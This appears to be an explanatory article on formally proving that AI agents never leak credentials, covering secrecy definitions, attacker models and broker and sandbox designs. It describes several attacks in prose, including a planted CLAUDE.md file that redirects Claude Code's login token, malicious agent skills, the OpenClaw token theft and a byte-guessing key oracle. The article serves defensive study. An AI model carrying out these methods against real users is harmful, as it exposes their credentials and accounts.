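# Formal verification that AI agents never send stored credentials to untrusted destinations

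## How do AI agents get credentials, and how do the credentials leak?

AI agents send email, push code and query databases for their users. To do so they need credentials, which are data, such as an API key or an access token, that a service accepts as proof of authority. An attacker who steers an agent can try to make it send those credentials away. Developers mostly respond with instructions to the model, filters and tests. A smaller group of researchers tries to prove mathematically that the system never sends a credential to an untrusted destination, meaning any channel or recipient not allowed to receive that particular credential. Their methods come from older work on cryptographic protocols, operating systems and programming languages. How well these methods work for agents depends heavily on where an agent's credentials are kept and which parts of the system can access them.

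### From a user's request to a tool call

An agent consists of a language model and a runtime, the software that lets the model call tools. The model only turns input text into output text. The runtime supplies the input, which consists of the user's request and a list of tools, with a description of what each tool does and which arguments it takes. Suppose a user asks the agent to file a bug report on GitHub, a service that hosts source code. The model outputs a tool call, a short structured text that names a tool for creating reports and fills in a title and a body. Nothing happens outside the model until the runtime reads the call and runs the matching code, which sends a request over the internet to GitHub. The runtime adds GitHub's reply to the model's input, and the model then makes another call or answers the user.

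GitHub will create the report only if the request carries a credential. The model can write the call without one, so another component has to attach it, unless the developer has put the credential where the model can read it. Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026) observe in *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* that the user who requested the task, the component that chose the action, the runtime that holds the credentials and the service that receives the request may all be separate parties. GitHub receives a valid token but cannot tell whether the user wanted the request. Security researchers call this the confused deputy problem, in which a program with legitimate authority uses it for someone who has none. Many tools are open to this problem. A study that Surapani and colleagues cite counted 177,436 of them, created between November 2024 and February 2026, in public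 repositories for the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting models to tools.

### What the credentials are and where they sit

An API key is a string that a service issues to a customer, whose software sends it with every request. OAuth 2.0 is a standard that lets a user authorize an application to act at another service without giving the application a password. The service issues an access token, which usually expires and covers a limited set of actions, and often a refresh token that the application can use to get new access tokens. Agents also handle database passwords, session cookies and private keys for logging in to servers or signing data.

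Most of these are bearer credentials, which work for anyone who has them. An API key has to be sent with each request, so any recipient can reuse it, whereas the owner of a private signing key can keep the key and send only signatures. *Bots exploited leaked AWS key from Docker image in under 8 seconds* (Help Net Security, 2026) describes an experiment by Billy Tsouvalas and Nick Nikiforakis of Stony Brook University that measured how quickly strangers use leaked keys. They planted working keys for Amazon's cloud service, OpenAI and Anthropic in 300 decoy software packages on public registries. In the first round of 100 packages, the median time before a bot used an Amazon key was 51 seconds, and all the Amazon keys had been used within 15 minutes. Revoking a key after noticing a leak will therefore often be too late. Narrow permissions helped more, since no bot ran up charges on the OpenAI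 and Anthropic keys that the researchers had restricted.

Many runtimes pass credentials to the agent through configuration files on disk or through environment variables, which are named values that the operating system gives a program when it starts. Any code that runs with the agent's privileges can generally read both. Users also paste keys into the prompt. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) traces how copies then spread into conversation history, logs, memory stores, generated code and error messages, most of which are meant to retain data.

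Agent software sometimes saves credentials without anyone intending it. When a user of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, approves a command with "Yes, and don't ask again", the program saves the exact command, including any password in it, to a settings file in the project folder. The security company Apiiro found 2,539 secrets in public copies of such files on GitHub, according to Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners' secrets on GitHub*. Recorded agent sessions can also expose credentials. Network Security Magazine's *Cursor Says Stolen Fireworks AI Key Led to Trojanized Claude Code Extension*, a second-hand account of a disclosure by the code-editor company Cursor, describes an attacker who copied recorded sessions, found unredacted credentials in some of them and used those to enter online services that Cursor relied on.

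A vault, or secret manager, is a service that stores credentials, controls who may fetch them and helps to replace them regularly. It protects a credential in storage, but once an agent fetches the credential, the agent holds it as it would any other. *SUDP* (Yu, Geng and colleagues, 2026) calls the prevailing pattern "authorization by exposure", because developers enable an action by placing a reusable secret inside the runtime. The main alternative is a broker, a trusted component that holds the credential and makes the authenticated call on the agent's behalf.

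### From an injected instruction to an outgoing request

Agents read web pages, emails and files written by strangers. In a prompt injection attack, someone places instructions in this content, and the model may follow them as if the user had given them. The attack is possible because the model receives both the user's request and the stranger's content as text and has no reliable way to separate them. Yu and colleagues give the example of a coding agent that holds a GitHub token and reads a project's README file, where a hidden instruction leads it to push code to a public repository.

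In a case from October 2026, Gal Weizman and Omer Samet of the company Forever Security noticed that a website can save a file to a computer's Downloads folder without a click, and that coding agents treat certain file names as project instructions. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder* (2026) reports that they wrote a file named CLAUDE.md, which Claude Code reads when a user starts Claude Code in that folder. The file presented a small settings change as a company's internal gateway. If the agent saved the change, Claude Code would send its requests for the Anthropic model, each carrying the user's login token, to a server the attacker chose. The researchers replayed a token captured this way against Anthropic's service, which treated them as the victim.

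In this attack, the model only has to write a new address into a settings file. The client code attaches the token to every request as usual, so the token goes to the new address. The model never has to see the token, so a filter that searched the model's output for strings resembling keys would have found nothing.

Claude Code normally asks a person to approve such a change and often refuses suspicious ones. The attack succeeded in about half of the researchers' tests, but it remains a demonstration. The file that Forever found on a customer's computer targeted OpenAI's Codex and tried to install a malicious package, but Forever's software blocked it.

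### Audits and documented flaws

The broadest measurement so far is of agent skills, add-on packages that combine written instructions for the model with scripts for it to run. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (Chen, Zhang et al., 2026) covers a random sample of 17,022 of the 170,226 skills on SkillsMP, a public marketplace, as of 12 February 2026. Keyword searches and code analysis narrowed the sample to 3,156 candidates. The team ran each candidate with Claude Code in an isolated container stocked with fake, individually marked credentials, and recorded network traffic, file writes and printed output. Each candidate ran three times on its advertised task and three times with a hostile instruction hidden in content it processed. Three reviewers examined the 1,427 skills that behaved suspiciously and confirmed leaks in 520, about 3.1% of the original sample. They attributed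 437 of these to negligence and 83 to malice.

Chen and colleagues define a leak as any exposure of a credential to a recipient or channel that the skill neither declares nor needs, which covers much more than theft. In 394 of the 520 skills, the credential appeared in printed output or logs, often because a developer had left a debugging statement in the code. One skill for Google's office software printed both the access token and the refresh token. This would be a minor lapse on an ordinary server, but agent runtimes feed printed output back into the model's input, where an attacker can request the credential through a later prompt injection. Only 68 skills sent credentials to an attacker-controlled address. One malicious skill advertised weather forecasts, but its script read the user's credential file and posted it to a stranger's server.

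Chen and colleagues describe 466 skills as leaking during normal execution, but by their own run counts, 237 of the 520 leaked in at most one of the three ordinary runs and were included only because of the hostile runs. The total may also be too low, because the code analysis did not follow keys that passed through an intermediate variable. Prevalence may differ on other marketplaces.

Some flaws that leak credentials do not involve the model. One was in OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant agent, parts of which have formal models. Its owner controls it through a web page that stores a token for the gateway, the local server behind the agent. OSV's *GHSA-g8p2-7wf7-98mq* (2026), the advisory for CVE-2026-25253, describes how the page took the gateway's address from the link that opened it, then connected to that address on loading and sent the stored token without checking where the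 address led. An attacker could therefore steal the token by getting the owner to click a link containing the address of the attacker's server.

With the token, the attacker could connect to the victim's real gateway, change its safety settings and run code on the machine. The attack worked even when the gateway accepted connections only from the same computer, because the victim's browser made the outgoing connection. The advisory rates the severity 8.8 out of 10. The corrected version, dated 30 January 2026 (The Hacker News, 2026), requires users to confirm a new gateway address. In July, GitLab's *GHSA-grc3-2j34-p6gm* (2026) recorded a related flaw in which the model's output could choose which address on the same machine received the gateway credentials.

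A later flaw affected Docker Sandboxes, which keeps keys away from the agent. It runs coding agents in isolated virtual machines, while a proxy outside them adds the real key to outgoing requests. In Endor Labs' *CVE-2026-136998* (30 November 2026), Peyton Kennedy reported that a third-party agent kit (a packaged configuration) could get the developer's approval honestly once and then redirect the key through an update. According to Docker's description, reproduced in Intruder's *CVE-2026-136998* (2026), the software recorded the approved destinations but did not enforce them when the proxy inserted the key. Thirteen services shared the faulty code, including OpenAI, Anthropic and GitHub. SC Media's *Docker sandboxes vulnerability exposes developer API keys* (2026) adds that the security logs did not show that the proxy had put a key into the request. Kennedy's demonstration used a test key,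 and PCQuest's *AI API keys at risk* notes that the findings do not confirm widespread exploitation.

### Why instructions and tests cannot support the word "never"

The easiest defence to add is an instruction telling the model never to reveal a credential. The model receives that instruction as text, along with any text the attacker supplies. Training can make the model more likely to follow the developer's instruction, but can't guarantee it. Weizman and Samet found that Codex ran the planted malware in more than 90% of attempts, while Claude Code was fooled about half the time. Instructions to the model also can't protect against a flaw like the one in OpenClaw's control page, which didn't involve a model.

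Testing can't show that an agent never sends a credential to an untrusted destination, because each test examines only one run, and later runs may involve inputs that nobody has yet written. Kenney and colleagues at Corvic AI tested the company's credential vault with 16 probes. They searched the agent's environment and files for the key, and sent requests to unrelated services and to sites that echo back whatever they receive. All 16 probes gave the expected secure outcome. The researchers call the study a functional evaluation and say it provides no formal guarantee. They also list attacks they did not try, such as chains of redirects and the compromise of a permitted destination.

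Simple arithmetic supports their caution. If the 16 probes had been random draws from the attacks that the vault will face, a true failure rate of 17% would still produce 16 straight passes about one time in twenty, since 0.83^16 ≈ 0.05. More passes would lower this upper bound on the failure rate, but not to zero. The assumption of random draws is also too optimistic, because an attacker looks for whatever the tests left out. Yu and colleagues cite evaluations in which attacks bypassed published behavioural defences by adapting to them. Attackers can also try many times. If a defence stops 99.9% of independent attempts, the probability that at least one of 1,000 attempts succeeds is 1 − 0.999^1000, or about 63%.

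### Formal verification and its tools

Formal verification uses mathematical proof to show that a system has a stated property. An engineer describes the system mathematically, typically as a set of possible states and the steps between them, defines the property in the same terms, and proves that every possible sequence of steps satisfies it. The proof can allow for any output from the language model, so nobody has to predict what the model will write. The proof may be about an abstract design or the program code itself, but a proof about a design does not carry over to code that departs from it.

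A theorem prover is a program for constructing and checking such proofs. In interactive provers such as Lean, Isabelle and Rocq (formerly Coq), a person sets out the argument, automated procedures fill in routine steps, and a small core program checks each inference. The resulting proof can cover infinitely many cases, such as any number of keys and tool calls. Producing it takes skilled labour, sometimes a great deal.

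A model checker searches the reachable states of a model and either reports that none violates the property or produces a counterexample, the exact sequence of steps that leads to the violation. This takes much less human effort, and the counterexamples help engineers find design errors. To keep the search finite, however, engineers often have to fix the sizes involved, say two agents and three keys. The result then holds for those sizes, and larger systems need a separate argument.

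The trusted base is everything that must be correct for a proved guarantee to hold in the running system. It includes the checking program and the assumptions of the proof. For a proof about credentials, it often also includes the operating system, the compiler, the cryptographic library and the list of destinations to which each key may go. If that list includes a wrong destination, a key can be sent there without contradicting the theorem.

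## What would "never sends a credential to an untrusted destination" mean as a theorem?

To state this as a theorem, an engineer has to define its words mathematically. "Never" is the easiest to define: it means "in no run", where a run is any sequence of states and events that begins in a permitted starting state and follows the system's rules. "Untrusted" and "sends" are harder, because some natural readings make the theorem true even of systems that leak credentials.

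### Which destinations are untrusted?

Let send(d, m) be the event that the system sends message m to destination d, and let Allowed(k) be the set of destinations that may receive credential k. A destination is untrusted for k if it is not in Allowed(k). Each credential needs its own set because a single list of trusted hosts that let GitHub receive the user's GitHub token would also let it receive the user's Amazon key, which it has no reason to receive.

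*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies the same idea to all the data an agent handles. Each item has a label listing its permitted readers, and anything derived from two items may go only to readers on both lists. A message containing a GitHub token and an Amazon key could therefore go only to a destination that may receive both, and usually no such destination exists. A tool call may send data through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel may read the data, so a group chat can become an untrusted destination when a stranger joins.

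A host name often doesn't describe a destination precisely enough. A policy that trusted a whole machine would permit the gateway flaw that GitLab recorded in July, because the credentials went to another address on the same machine. The path also matters, since an OAuth refresh token should go only to the address that issues new tokens. The attacker may also have an account at an allowed host. An agent that writes its GitHub token into the text of a public bug report has sent it to the right host, but the host then shows it to everyone. An entry in Allowed(k) might therefore be "the authorization header of a request to api.github.com, port 443".

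### From literal copies to trace secrecy

The most direct reading of the sentence is that no message to an untrusted destination contains the key:

*For every run, every credential k and every event send(d, m) in the run: if d ∉ Allowed(k), then k does not occur in m.*

Base64 encoding defeats this property if "occur" means that the key's exact characters appear in the message. Base64 is a standard way to write any data using 64 common characters, and programs routinely use it in emails and web requests. It turns the made-up key `sk-42` into `c2stNDI=`. The encoded string does not contain the original key, so an agent could send it to a stranger without violating the property, and the stranger could decode it instantly. Reversing the key or splitting it between two messages also defeats the property.

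If "occur" also covers encrypted content, the property becomes too strict. It would rule out a normal request to GitHub, because the encrypted token passes through network equipment owned by strangers, even though they cannot read it. A better definition is based on what outsiders can work out from the messages they receive.

Let Seen(τ, k) be all the messages that parties outside Allowed(k) observe in run τ, including any encrypted traffic they can intercept. Let Known be what they know at the start, and let Derive(M) be everything they can compute from a set of messages M. Trace secrecy is then the following property:

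*For every run τ and every credential k: k ∉ Derive(Known ∪ Seen(τ, k)).*

The theorem would be that no run ever gives the attacker enough to construct the key. *Relating two standard notions of secrecy* (Cortier, Rusinowitch and Zălinescu, 2007) calls this syntactic secrecy. The attacker can join messages and take them apart, encrypt with any known key, and decrypt with the right one. A message is derivable exactly when some combination of these operations, applied to public values and observed messages, produces it.

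The list has to be complete. If it includes base64 decoding, sending `c2stNDI=` violates trace secrecy. If the engineer leaves decoding out, the proof may succeed for a system that leaks every key in base64. Cortier and colleagues faced a similar choice with digital signatures, some of which reveal part of the signed message. They let the attacker recover the whole message from any signature, which can only make a secrecy proof harder.

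Trace secrecy is a common target in protocol verification. In *Bridging Theory and Practice*, Tudorache, Kurtev and van den Brand (2026) reviewed 53 recent studies that used ProVerif or Tamarin, two programs that verify cryptographic protocols automatically. Confidentiality properties appeared 35 times, second only to authentication with 38. The basic formula for confidentiality is secret(x) ⇒ ¬K(x), where K(x) means that the attacker knows x.

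### Explicit secrecy

Agents and their tools are ordinary programs that can transform a key in so many ways that a complete list of operations is hard to write. Developers often use taint tracking instead. They mark the secret, let the mark spread to everything computed from it, and block marked data from leaving. *Explicit Secrecy* (Schoepe, Balliu and colleagues, 2016) observed that this technique had no general definition of what it guarantees, and proposed one.

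Their definition starts from a run of the program. From this run, take only the steps that change data or send output, in order, and leave out every test and branch. Call the resulting sequence f. Then execute f from different starting states and compare what it sends to destinations outside Allowed(k):

*For every run with data steps f, and all starting states s and s′ that differ only in k: out(f(s)) = out(f(s′)).*

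Sending the key k in base64 violates explicit secrecy, even if the definition doesn't mention base64. The sequence f contains the step "encode k and send the result", so a different key produces a different output.

However, explicit secrecy doesn't cover anything a program reveals through its choice of steps. For example, a program can test each character of the key and, in the matching branch, append that character to a message as a constant. In a run with the key `sk-42`, the data steps append "s", then "k", and so on, then send the message. Those same steps would send `sk-42` whatever the key was, so the program has explicit secrecy even though it sent the whole key. Schoepe and colleagues acknowledge that taint tracking is unsound for this reason, especially against malicious code, but it is much easier to apply than methods that follow branches.

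The result also depends on which parts of the system count as data and which as control. Schoepe and colleagues point out that counting everything as control makes the property trivially true, while counting everything as data gives a form of noninterference. Costa and colleagues, in their version for agents, count the tools' stored data as data and the conversation with the model as control. If a tool puts a key into the conversation and the model copies it into an email, the email's text counts as a constant, so the leak does not violate the definition. Their label checks would still block the email if the key is labelled confidential, so in this case the mechanism is stricter than the property they prove for it.

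### Noninterference

Noninterference requires that the attacker's observations do not depend on the key at all. Let i stand for everything else that affects the run, including the user's request, the web pages the agent reads, the attacker's messages and the model's random choices. View(i, k) is everything the attacker observes when the key is k:

*For all inputs i and all keys k and k′: View(i, k) = View(i, k′).*

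The character-copying program fails this test because changing the key changes the message. A fair comparison must also change the key at the service that accepts it. Otherwise the key in the second run would be invalid, the service would refuse the request, and an attacker who could see whether the bug report appeared could tell the two runs apart.

Exact equality is too strict when the attacker can see encrypted traffic, because encrypted messages change with their content. Protocol researchers therefore require only that the attacker cannot tell the two runs apart. Cortier and colleagues call this strong secrecy and prove that it implies trace secrecy. If the attacker could compute the key from observed messages, he could apply the same computation in both runs and tell them apart by the different results.

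Neither explicit secrecy nor noninterference implies the other. Schoepe and colleagues give the example of a program that outputs a secret number if it is zero, and otherwise outputs zero. The output is always zero, so the program satisfies noninterference. It violates explicit secrecy because one of its runs contains the step "output the secret".

Noninterference is often impractical for agents. Costa and colleagues argue that enforcing it would essentially forbid any tool call with publicly visible effects after the agent has called a tool that may read confidential data. For example, an agent that had read a private email could no longer post anything publicly.

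### A component that never outputs the key but reveals it

Suppose a tool holds a 32-byte key and answers yes or no to questions of the form "Is byte i equal to g?" It never outputs any part of the key. But a byte has only 256 possible values, so an attacker can find each byte with at most 256 questions and the whole key with at most 256 × 32 = 8,192. At 100 questions a second, this takes less than a minute and a half. Guessing the whole key at once could take up to 256^32 attempts, or about 10^77. A file-search tool that reports only whether a pattern matched poses the same risk if the file holds a key, because an injected instruction can make the agent try one character at a time.

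| Property | Rules out sending the key in base64? | Rules out answering byte guesses? |
|---|---|---|
| No literal copy in a message | No | No |
| Trace secrecy, with the key as a single symbol | Yes, if the model includes decoding | No |
| Explicit secrecy | Yes | Only if the code computes the answer as a value |
| Noninterference | Yes | Yes |

Trace secrecy permits the guessing because protocol models usually represent a key as one indivisible symbol. The attacker receives only "yes" and "no", and no operation turns these into the symbol. Cortier and colleagues give a similar example of a protocol that compares the secret with a known value and sends "ok" if they match. This protocol has trace secrecy but not strong secrecy.

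Dividing the symbol into 32 bytes would not help. All 256 byte values are public, so the attacker could "derive" every possible key by joining bytes, and trace secrecy would fail for every system. The attacker learns from the answers which of these strings is the right one. Cryptographers handle this with probabilities. In their models, messages are strings of bits and the attacker is an algorithm with limited computing time. The key is secret if the attacker has only a negligible chance of outputting it. The guessing tool fails that definition.

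With explicit secrecy, the result depends on how the programmer wrote the tool. If the code branches on whether byte i equals g and sends "yes" in one branch and "no" in the other, each run sends a constant and the property holds. If the code computes the truth value of the comparison and sends that value, the property fails, although both versions behave identically. *An Empirical Study of Information Flows in Real-World JavaScript* (2019) describes an intermediate property called observable secrecy, which keeps the tests and removes only the code inside branches that the run did not take. Both versions of the tool violate it. A tool that replies only to correct guesses can still satisfy it in a run where every guess is wrong, even though each missing reply rules out a value.

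A single query shows that the tool violates noninterference, because asking whether byte i has the first key's value gives different answers for two keys that differ in that byte. The same argument applies to a tool that only confirms complete 32-byte guesses, which is harmless in practice. Noninterference does not measure how much the attacker learns, so engineers often have to declare exceptions. Schoepe and colleagues allow for these in explicit secrecy by letting the attacker's knowledge grow only at designated release events. A settings page that displays the last four characters of a key would need such an exception. Someone still has to judge whether each exception is safe, because the byte-guessing tool would pass if its answers counted as permitted releases.

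The definition of View matters too. Suppose a service gives every wrong key the same error message but stops comparing at the first wrong byte. Its response takes slightly longer when more of the leading bytes are right, so an attacker who can measure the delay can again guess the key byte by byte. A proof of noninterference does not rule out this attack if View leaves out timing. *Formalization of Security* (Barthe, 2026) describes a stricter policy for cryptographic code, called constant-time, which treats the outcome of every branch and the address of every memory access as visible to the attacker.

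### Properties of one run and properties of two

A violation of trace secrecy appears in a single run, at the first moment when the attacker can derive the key. A proof can rule out violations with an invariant, a statement that is true in the initial state and that every step preserves. If the invariant implies that the attacker cannot derive the key, no reachable state violates trace secrecy.

A single run cannot show that a tool violates noninterference. If the guessing tool answers "yes", it could be ignoring the key and always answering "yes". Only comparison with a second run that uses a different key can show that the answer depends on the key. A property of sets of runs is called a hyperproperty, and Barthe names noninterference as a typical example.

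The classic proof method for noninterference is unwinding, due to Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer. It begins with a relation s ~ t, meaning that the attacker cannot tell state s from state t. Barthe gives two basic lemmas, each of which holds under some additional conditions:

- If s ~ t, and one step leads from s to s′ and from t to t′, then s′ ~ t′.
- If a step leads from s to s′, then s ~ s′. This lemma is for steps that the attacker cannot observe.

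Together they extend the relation from single steps to whole runs. The relation works like an invariant over pairs of states. For a broker, the two states would be identical except for the key in the vault. When the broker adds the key to a request for an allowed service, the attacker sees the same thing in both cases and the states remain related. With the guessing tool, the same question produces "yes" from one state and "no" from the other, so the proof fails at that step.

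Cortier and colleagues found conditions under which trace secrecy, which is simpler to prove, implies strong secrecy. If the attacker only listens, all encryption must be randomized, the secret must never serve as a key for encryption or signing, and no message may result from taking the secret apart. Without randomized encryption, the attacker could encrypt guesses and compare the results with what he observed. If the attacker also sends messages, the main further condition is that the protocol never tests the secret. A broker that only forwards an API key inside encrypted requests might satisfy these conditions, but one that uses a private key to sign data would not.

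The difference between trace secrecy and noninterference also affects whether a proof about a design carries over to code. If every run of the code corresponds to a run of the design with the same messages, trace secrecy carries over, but noninterference may not. Suppose the design lets a broker answer two requests in either order, and the code chooses the order according to one bit of the key. The design permits every run of the code, but the order reveals the bit. Barthe notes that, for this reason, the usual standard of compiler correctness does not preserve security properties in general.

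### Disclosing a key and misusing it

All four properties concern what outsiders learn about the key. Costa and colleagues distinguish attacks that extract data from attacks that abuse the powers a user has delegated to the agent. Suppose an instruction hidden in a README file makes an agent ask its broker to delete a code repository. The broker adds the token and sends the request to GitHub, which is an allowed destination. No outsider learns anything about the token, so the system can satisfy all four properties even though the user loses the repository.

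A theorem against misuse has to connect each use of a key to an earlier approval:

*For every run: if use(k, a) occurs at step j, then authorize(u, a) occurs at some step i < j.*

Here a is the exact action and u is a user entitled to approve it. This is a property of single runs, and it resembles what Tudorache and colleagues call agreement, in which one participant finishes an exchange only if the other took part with the same data. A stronger form, injective agreement, requires a separate start for each finish. For approvals, this would prevent an agent from making the same payment twice after a single approval.

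Neither kind of theorem implies the other. An agent could use a token only for approved actions and still print it in a public log. The value of the authorization theorem also depends on how it defines "authorize". If a user asks an agent to tidy up old repositories, someone has to decide whether that request authorizes deleting one, and only then can the formula apply.

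## What can the attacker do in these proofs?

Trace secrecy depends on which messages the attacker sees and what he can compute from them. It also depends on any messages he can send, because they change what the system does next. The attackers considered here range from the weakest, who controls only the network, to the strongest, who runs code of his choice on the machine that stores the key.

### An attacker who controls the network

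The standard attacker model comes from Dolev and Yao's *On the Security of Public Key Protocols* (1983). They observed that public-key encryption usually stops an eavesdropper who only listens, but a badly designed protocol can still fail against one who takes part in the protocol. Their attacker can obtain any message on the network. He is also a legitimate user, so he can start a conversation with anyone, and anyone may start one with him. The model assumes perfect cryptography, meaning nobody can decrypt a message without the right private key or tamper with the public list of encryption keys.

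One of their examples shows how much an attacker gains by taking part. Alice sends Bob a secret encrypted with Bob's public key, and Bob confirms by returning the secret encrypted with Alice's. The names of sender and receiver travel outside the encryption. The attack takes four steps:

1. The attacker intercepts Alice's message.
2. He replaces her name with his own and forwards the message to Bob.
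3. Bob follows the protocol and returns the secret encrypted with the attacker's public key.
4. The attacker decrypts it.

The attacker never breaks the encryption, because Bob decrypts the message for him. A credential broker could make the same mistake as Bob if it handled a secret for whoever the request named.

Putting the sender's name inside the encrypted text repairs the protocol, and Dolev and Yao prove that the repaired version is secure whatever the attacker does. They also show that adding another layer of encryption makes it insecure again, because the attacker can start two more conversations with Alice, and her reply in each one removes a layer.

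Later researchers wrote the attacker's abilities as explicit rules, which give an exact meaning to the set Derive in the definition of trace secrecy. Abadi and Blanchet, in *Analyzing Security Protocols with Secrecy Types and Logic Programs*, separate constructors, which build messages, from destructors, which open them:

| Anyone who has | can build | Rule for opening it |
|---|---|---|
| a message m and a shared key n | sencrypt(m, n) | n recovers m |
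| a message m and a public key pk(n) | pencrypt(m, pk(n)) | the private key n recovers m |
| a message m and a signing key n | sign(m, n) | anyone can recover m |
| a message m | the hash H(m) | none |

The attacker can apply these rules as often as he likes. Suppose an agent's log contains an API key encrypted with n. He cannot derive the API key from the log alone, but he can once an error message prints n.

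Leaving out a rule is also an assumption. No rule reverses a hash, so nobody in the model can ever recover a message from its hash. Ryan and Smyth (2010), in *Applied pi calculus*, note that this is far stronger than what cryptographers normally require of a hash function. Some operations can't be expressed as constructors or destructors. One is exclusive-or, a common way to combine two strings of bits, which Abadi and Blanchet have to treat separately.

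### Any process running in parallel

The applied pi calculus is a small language for describing programs that exchange messages. It represents the attacker as one more program. Programs in this language are called processes. They can send and receive messages on channels, compare values, run copies of themselves and create new names, which stand for fresh keys or private channels. Ryan and Smyth define secrecy for a system P and a secret M roughly as follows:

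*P keeps M secret if there is no process I, sharing none of P's private names, such that P and I running in parallel can output M on a public channel.*

"No process I" means no program that anyone could write in the language. Such a program can send any number of requests, remember all the replies, create its own keys and pose as several users at once. Every attack strategy is some process I, so nobody has to list the strategies in advance. If secrecy fails, some particular process I demonstrates the attack. Ryan and Smyth write out such a process for a key-exchange protocol, using three inputs and three outputs. Their attacker gets a server to sign a session key for it, then re-encrypts the signed key for a client. The client uses that key to encrypt its secret, so the attacker can read the secret.

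However, the attacker process I has only the names and channels it is given. Ryan and Smyth illustrate this with a process that creates a new secret s, reads a message from a public channel, and announces "got s" if the message equals s. No attacker can trigger the announcement. Even if the attacker sends a value it calls s, that value is different from the secret. If the process first publishes s encrypted with a key the attacker knows, the attacker can decrypt s and send it back, which triggers the announcement. If the process publishes only the hash of s, the attacker can send the hash to others but still cannot supply s.

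The same restriction applies to channels. In the calculus of *DeepSec* (2022), a paper on verifying security protocols, any output on a channel the attacker knows adds to his knowledge, and any input on such a channel comes from him. He can neither read nor write on a channel whose name he lacks. A simple broker then looks like this, where `c` is public and `k` is the API key:

```
new k; new d;
( repeat: in(c, x); out(d, (x, k))      broker
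| repeat: in(d, y); out(c, done) )      service
```

The broker receives a request x on the public channel, attaches the key and forwards both on the private channel d. The service replies "done". The key travels only on d, so no attacker process I can output it.

If the request also specifies the channel on which the broker forwards it, the attacker can create a channel, name it in a request, read the key from it and publish the key. OpenClaw's control page had this flaw.

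Secrecy is harder to check when the proof must cover every possible attacker. The 2017 tutorial *Formal Models and Techniques for Analyzing Security Protocols* gives a procedure that always decides secrecy when participants run a limited number of sessions, and shows that the problem is undecidable when the number is unlimited. Automatic tools can still prove many individual protocols secure. ProVerif, which Blanchet describes in *Modeling and Verifying Security Protocols with the Applied Pi Calculus and ProVerif*, can do so for any number of sessions.

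### Treating the agent as the attacker

A proof can treat the AI agent as the process I. The theorem already covers every possible I, so it holds whatever the model outputs, even if a prompt injection succeeds, the developer replaces the model with a worse one, or the model itself is malicious. A proof about PocketFlow, a small framework for building agents, likewise treats the language model as an oracle that may return anything. A proof could instead model the agent as an honest participant that carries out the user's request, but the engineer would then have to describe mathematically how a language model responds to hostile text, and nobody knows how to do this reliably.

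Yu and colleagues take this approach in SUDP, a protocol that lets an agent request operations that need a secret without ever receiving it. They place the agent outside the user's trust boundary, and their basic attacker controls both the agent and the network. The design proposed in *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, 2026) treats the model-driven process "and everything it spawns" as untrusted, but trusts the runtime that launches the agent and owns its network connections. The runtime reads the destination from the live encrypted connection, so the model can request an action but cannot choose the address for which the resulting signature is valid.

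The engineer has to treat everything the model can steer as under the attacker's control, including the commands it runs, the scripts it writes, the packages it installs and any file that a trusted component later reads. The attack through the Downloads folder relied on such a file. A proof that treated Claude Code's client as trusted, with a fixed address, would have missed it. If the proof lets the attacker write to the settings file, the attack appears as a counterexample.

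With this approach, the proof can't rely on anything the agent does well. The same theorem holds for an agent that refuses 99% of injected instructions and for one that obeys them all. If a user pastes a key into the prompt, the attacker has that key from the start, so it's impossible to prove that the key stays secret.

*Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (Bhardwaj, 2026) models the attacker as someone who publishes or alters agent skills. This attacker can intercept, inject, build, take apart and replay messages at every stage from a skill's author to the running agent. Bhardwaj states a theorem that the attacker is maximal, meaning that he can reproduce whatever any other symbolic attacker on this supply chain could do. The theorem compares only symbolic attackers, who follow rules of the Dolev-Yao kind. The model also includes what Bhardwaj calls a perfect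 sandbox assumption, by analogy with perfect cryptography.

### Why these theorems presuppose isolation

Suppose the broker model above had one more line:

```
| repeat: in(c, a); out(c, memory(a))
```

This process accepts a memory address on the public channel and returns the contents. The attacker sends the address of k and receives the key. No improvement to the broker can prevent this. Secrecy is false for any system in which an arbitrary process can read the memory or file that holds the key.

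The original model excludes the attack because processes in the calculus share only channels. On a real computer, programs that run under the same user account can usually read the same files, and on some systems they can read each other's memory. A secrecy proof for a broker therefore applies to a real computer only if something enforces the separation that is built into the calculus.

This separation was missing in a 2025 attack included in Ganesan's survey of incidents. Malicious versions of Nx, a tool for building software, collected 2,349 credentials from 1,079 developers' machines. They also ran AI command-line tools already on those machines to search for secrets. Even a perfect protocol between the developer's tools and GitHub would not have prevented the thefts, which Ganesan attributes to tokens and keys on disk that any local process could read.

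Assuming that sandboxes are perfect is also riskier than assuming that cryptography is. Another entry in the same survey describes attacks on coding agents in 2025 and 2026 that escaped sandboxes meant to restrict where the agents could write.

### Isolation by a browser kernel

A web browser has much the same problem as an agent runtime because it runs strangers' code on a machine that also stores session cookies, which are bearer credentials. *Establishing Browser Security Guarantees through Formal Shim Verification* (Jang, Tatlock and Lerner, 2012) presents Quark, a browser that runs each tab in a separate sandboxed process. A tab can reach the network, the screen and stored cookies only by sending a request to a small program called the browser kernel.

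The proofs assume that an attacker may have taken over any component exposed to web content except the kernel, including every tab and the processes that store cookies, and can run any code there. The kernel handles one request at a time. When a tab asks for a connection, the kernel compares the host with the domain that the user assigned to that tab, then either opens the connection or returns an error. Jang and colleagues prove in Coq that the kernel never lets a tab store or retrieve another domain's cookies, and that other tabs' requests do not affect the kernel's response to a tab.

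These proofs cover the kernel's actual code, whereas the designers of an earlier browser, OP, ran a model checker on an abstract model of their kernel, which left open whether the real program matched the model. Quark's kernel has 859 lines of code and needed 4,383 lines of proof. The browser engine running in the tabs has about 969,000 lines, which did not need to be verified. The project took about six person-months. Pages from ten popular sites loaded 24% more slowly on average in Quark than in an ordinary browser built on the same engine.

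The proofs still leave a large trusted base, including the operating system and the sandbox, which uses the Unix mechanism chroot to restrict a process to part of the file system. Jang and colleagues prove that the kernel handles each request correctly, but they assume that tabs cannot bypass the kernel. Security engineers call this complete mediation, meaning that every relevant action passes through the component that checks it.

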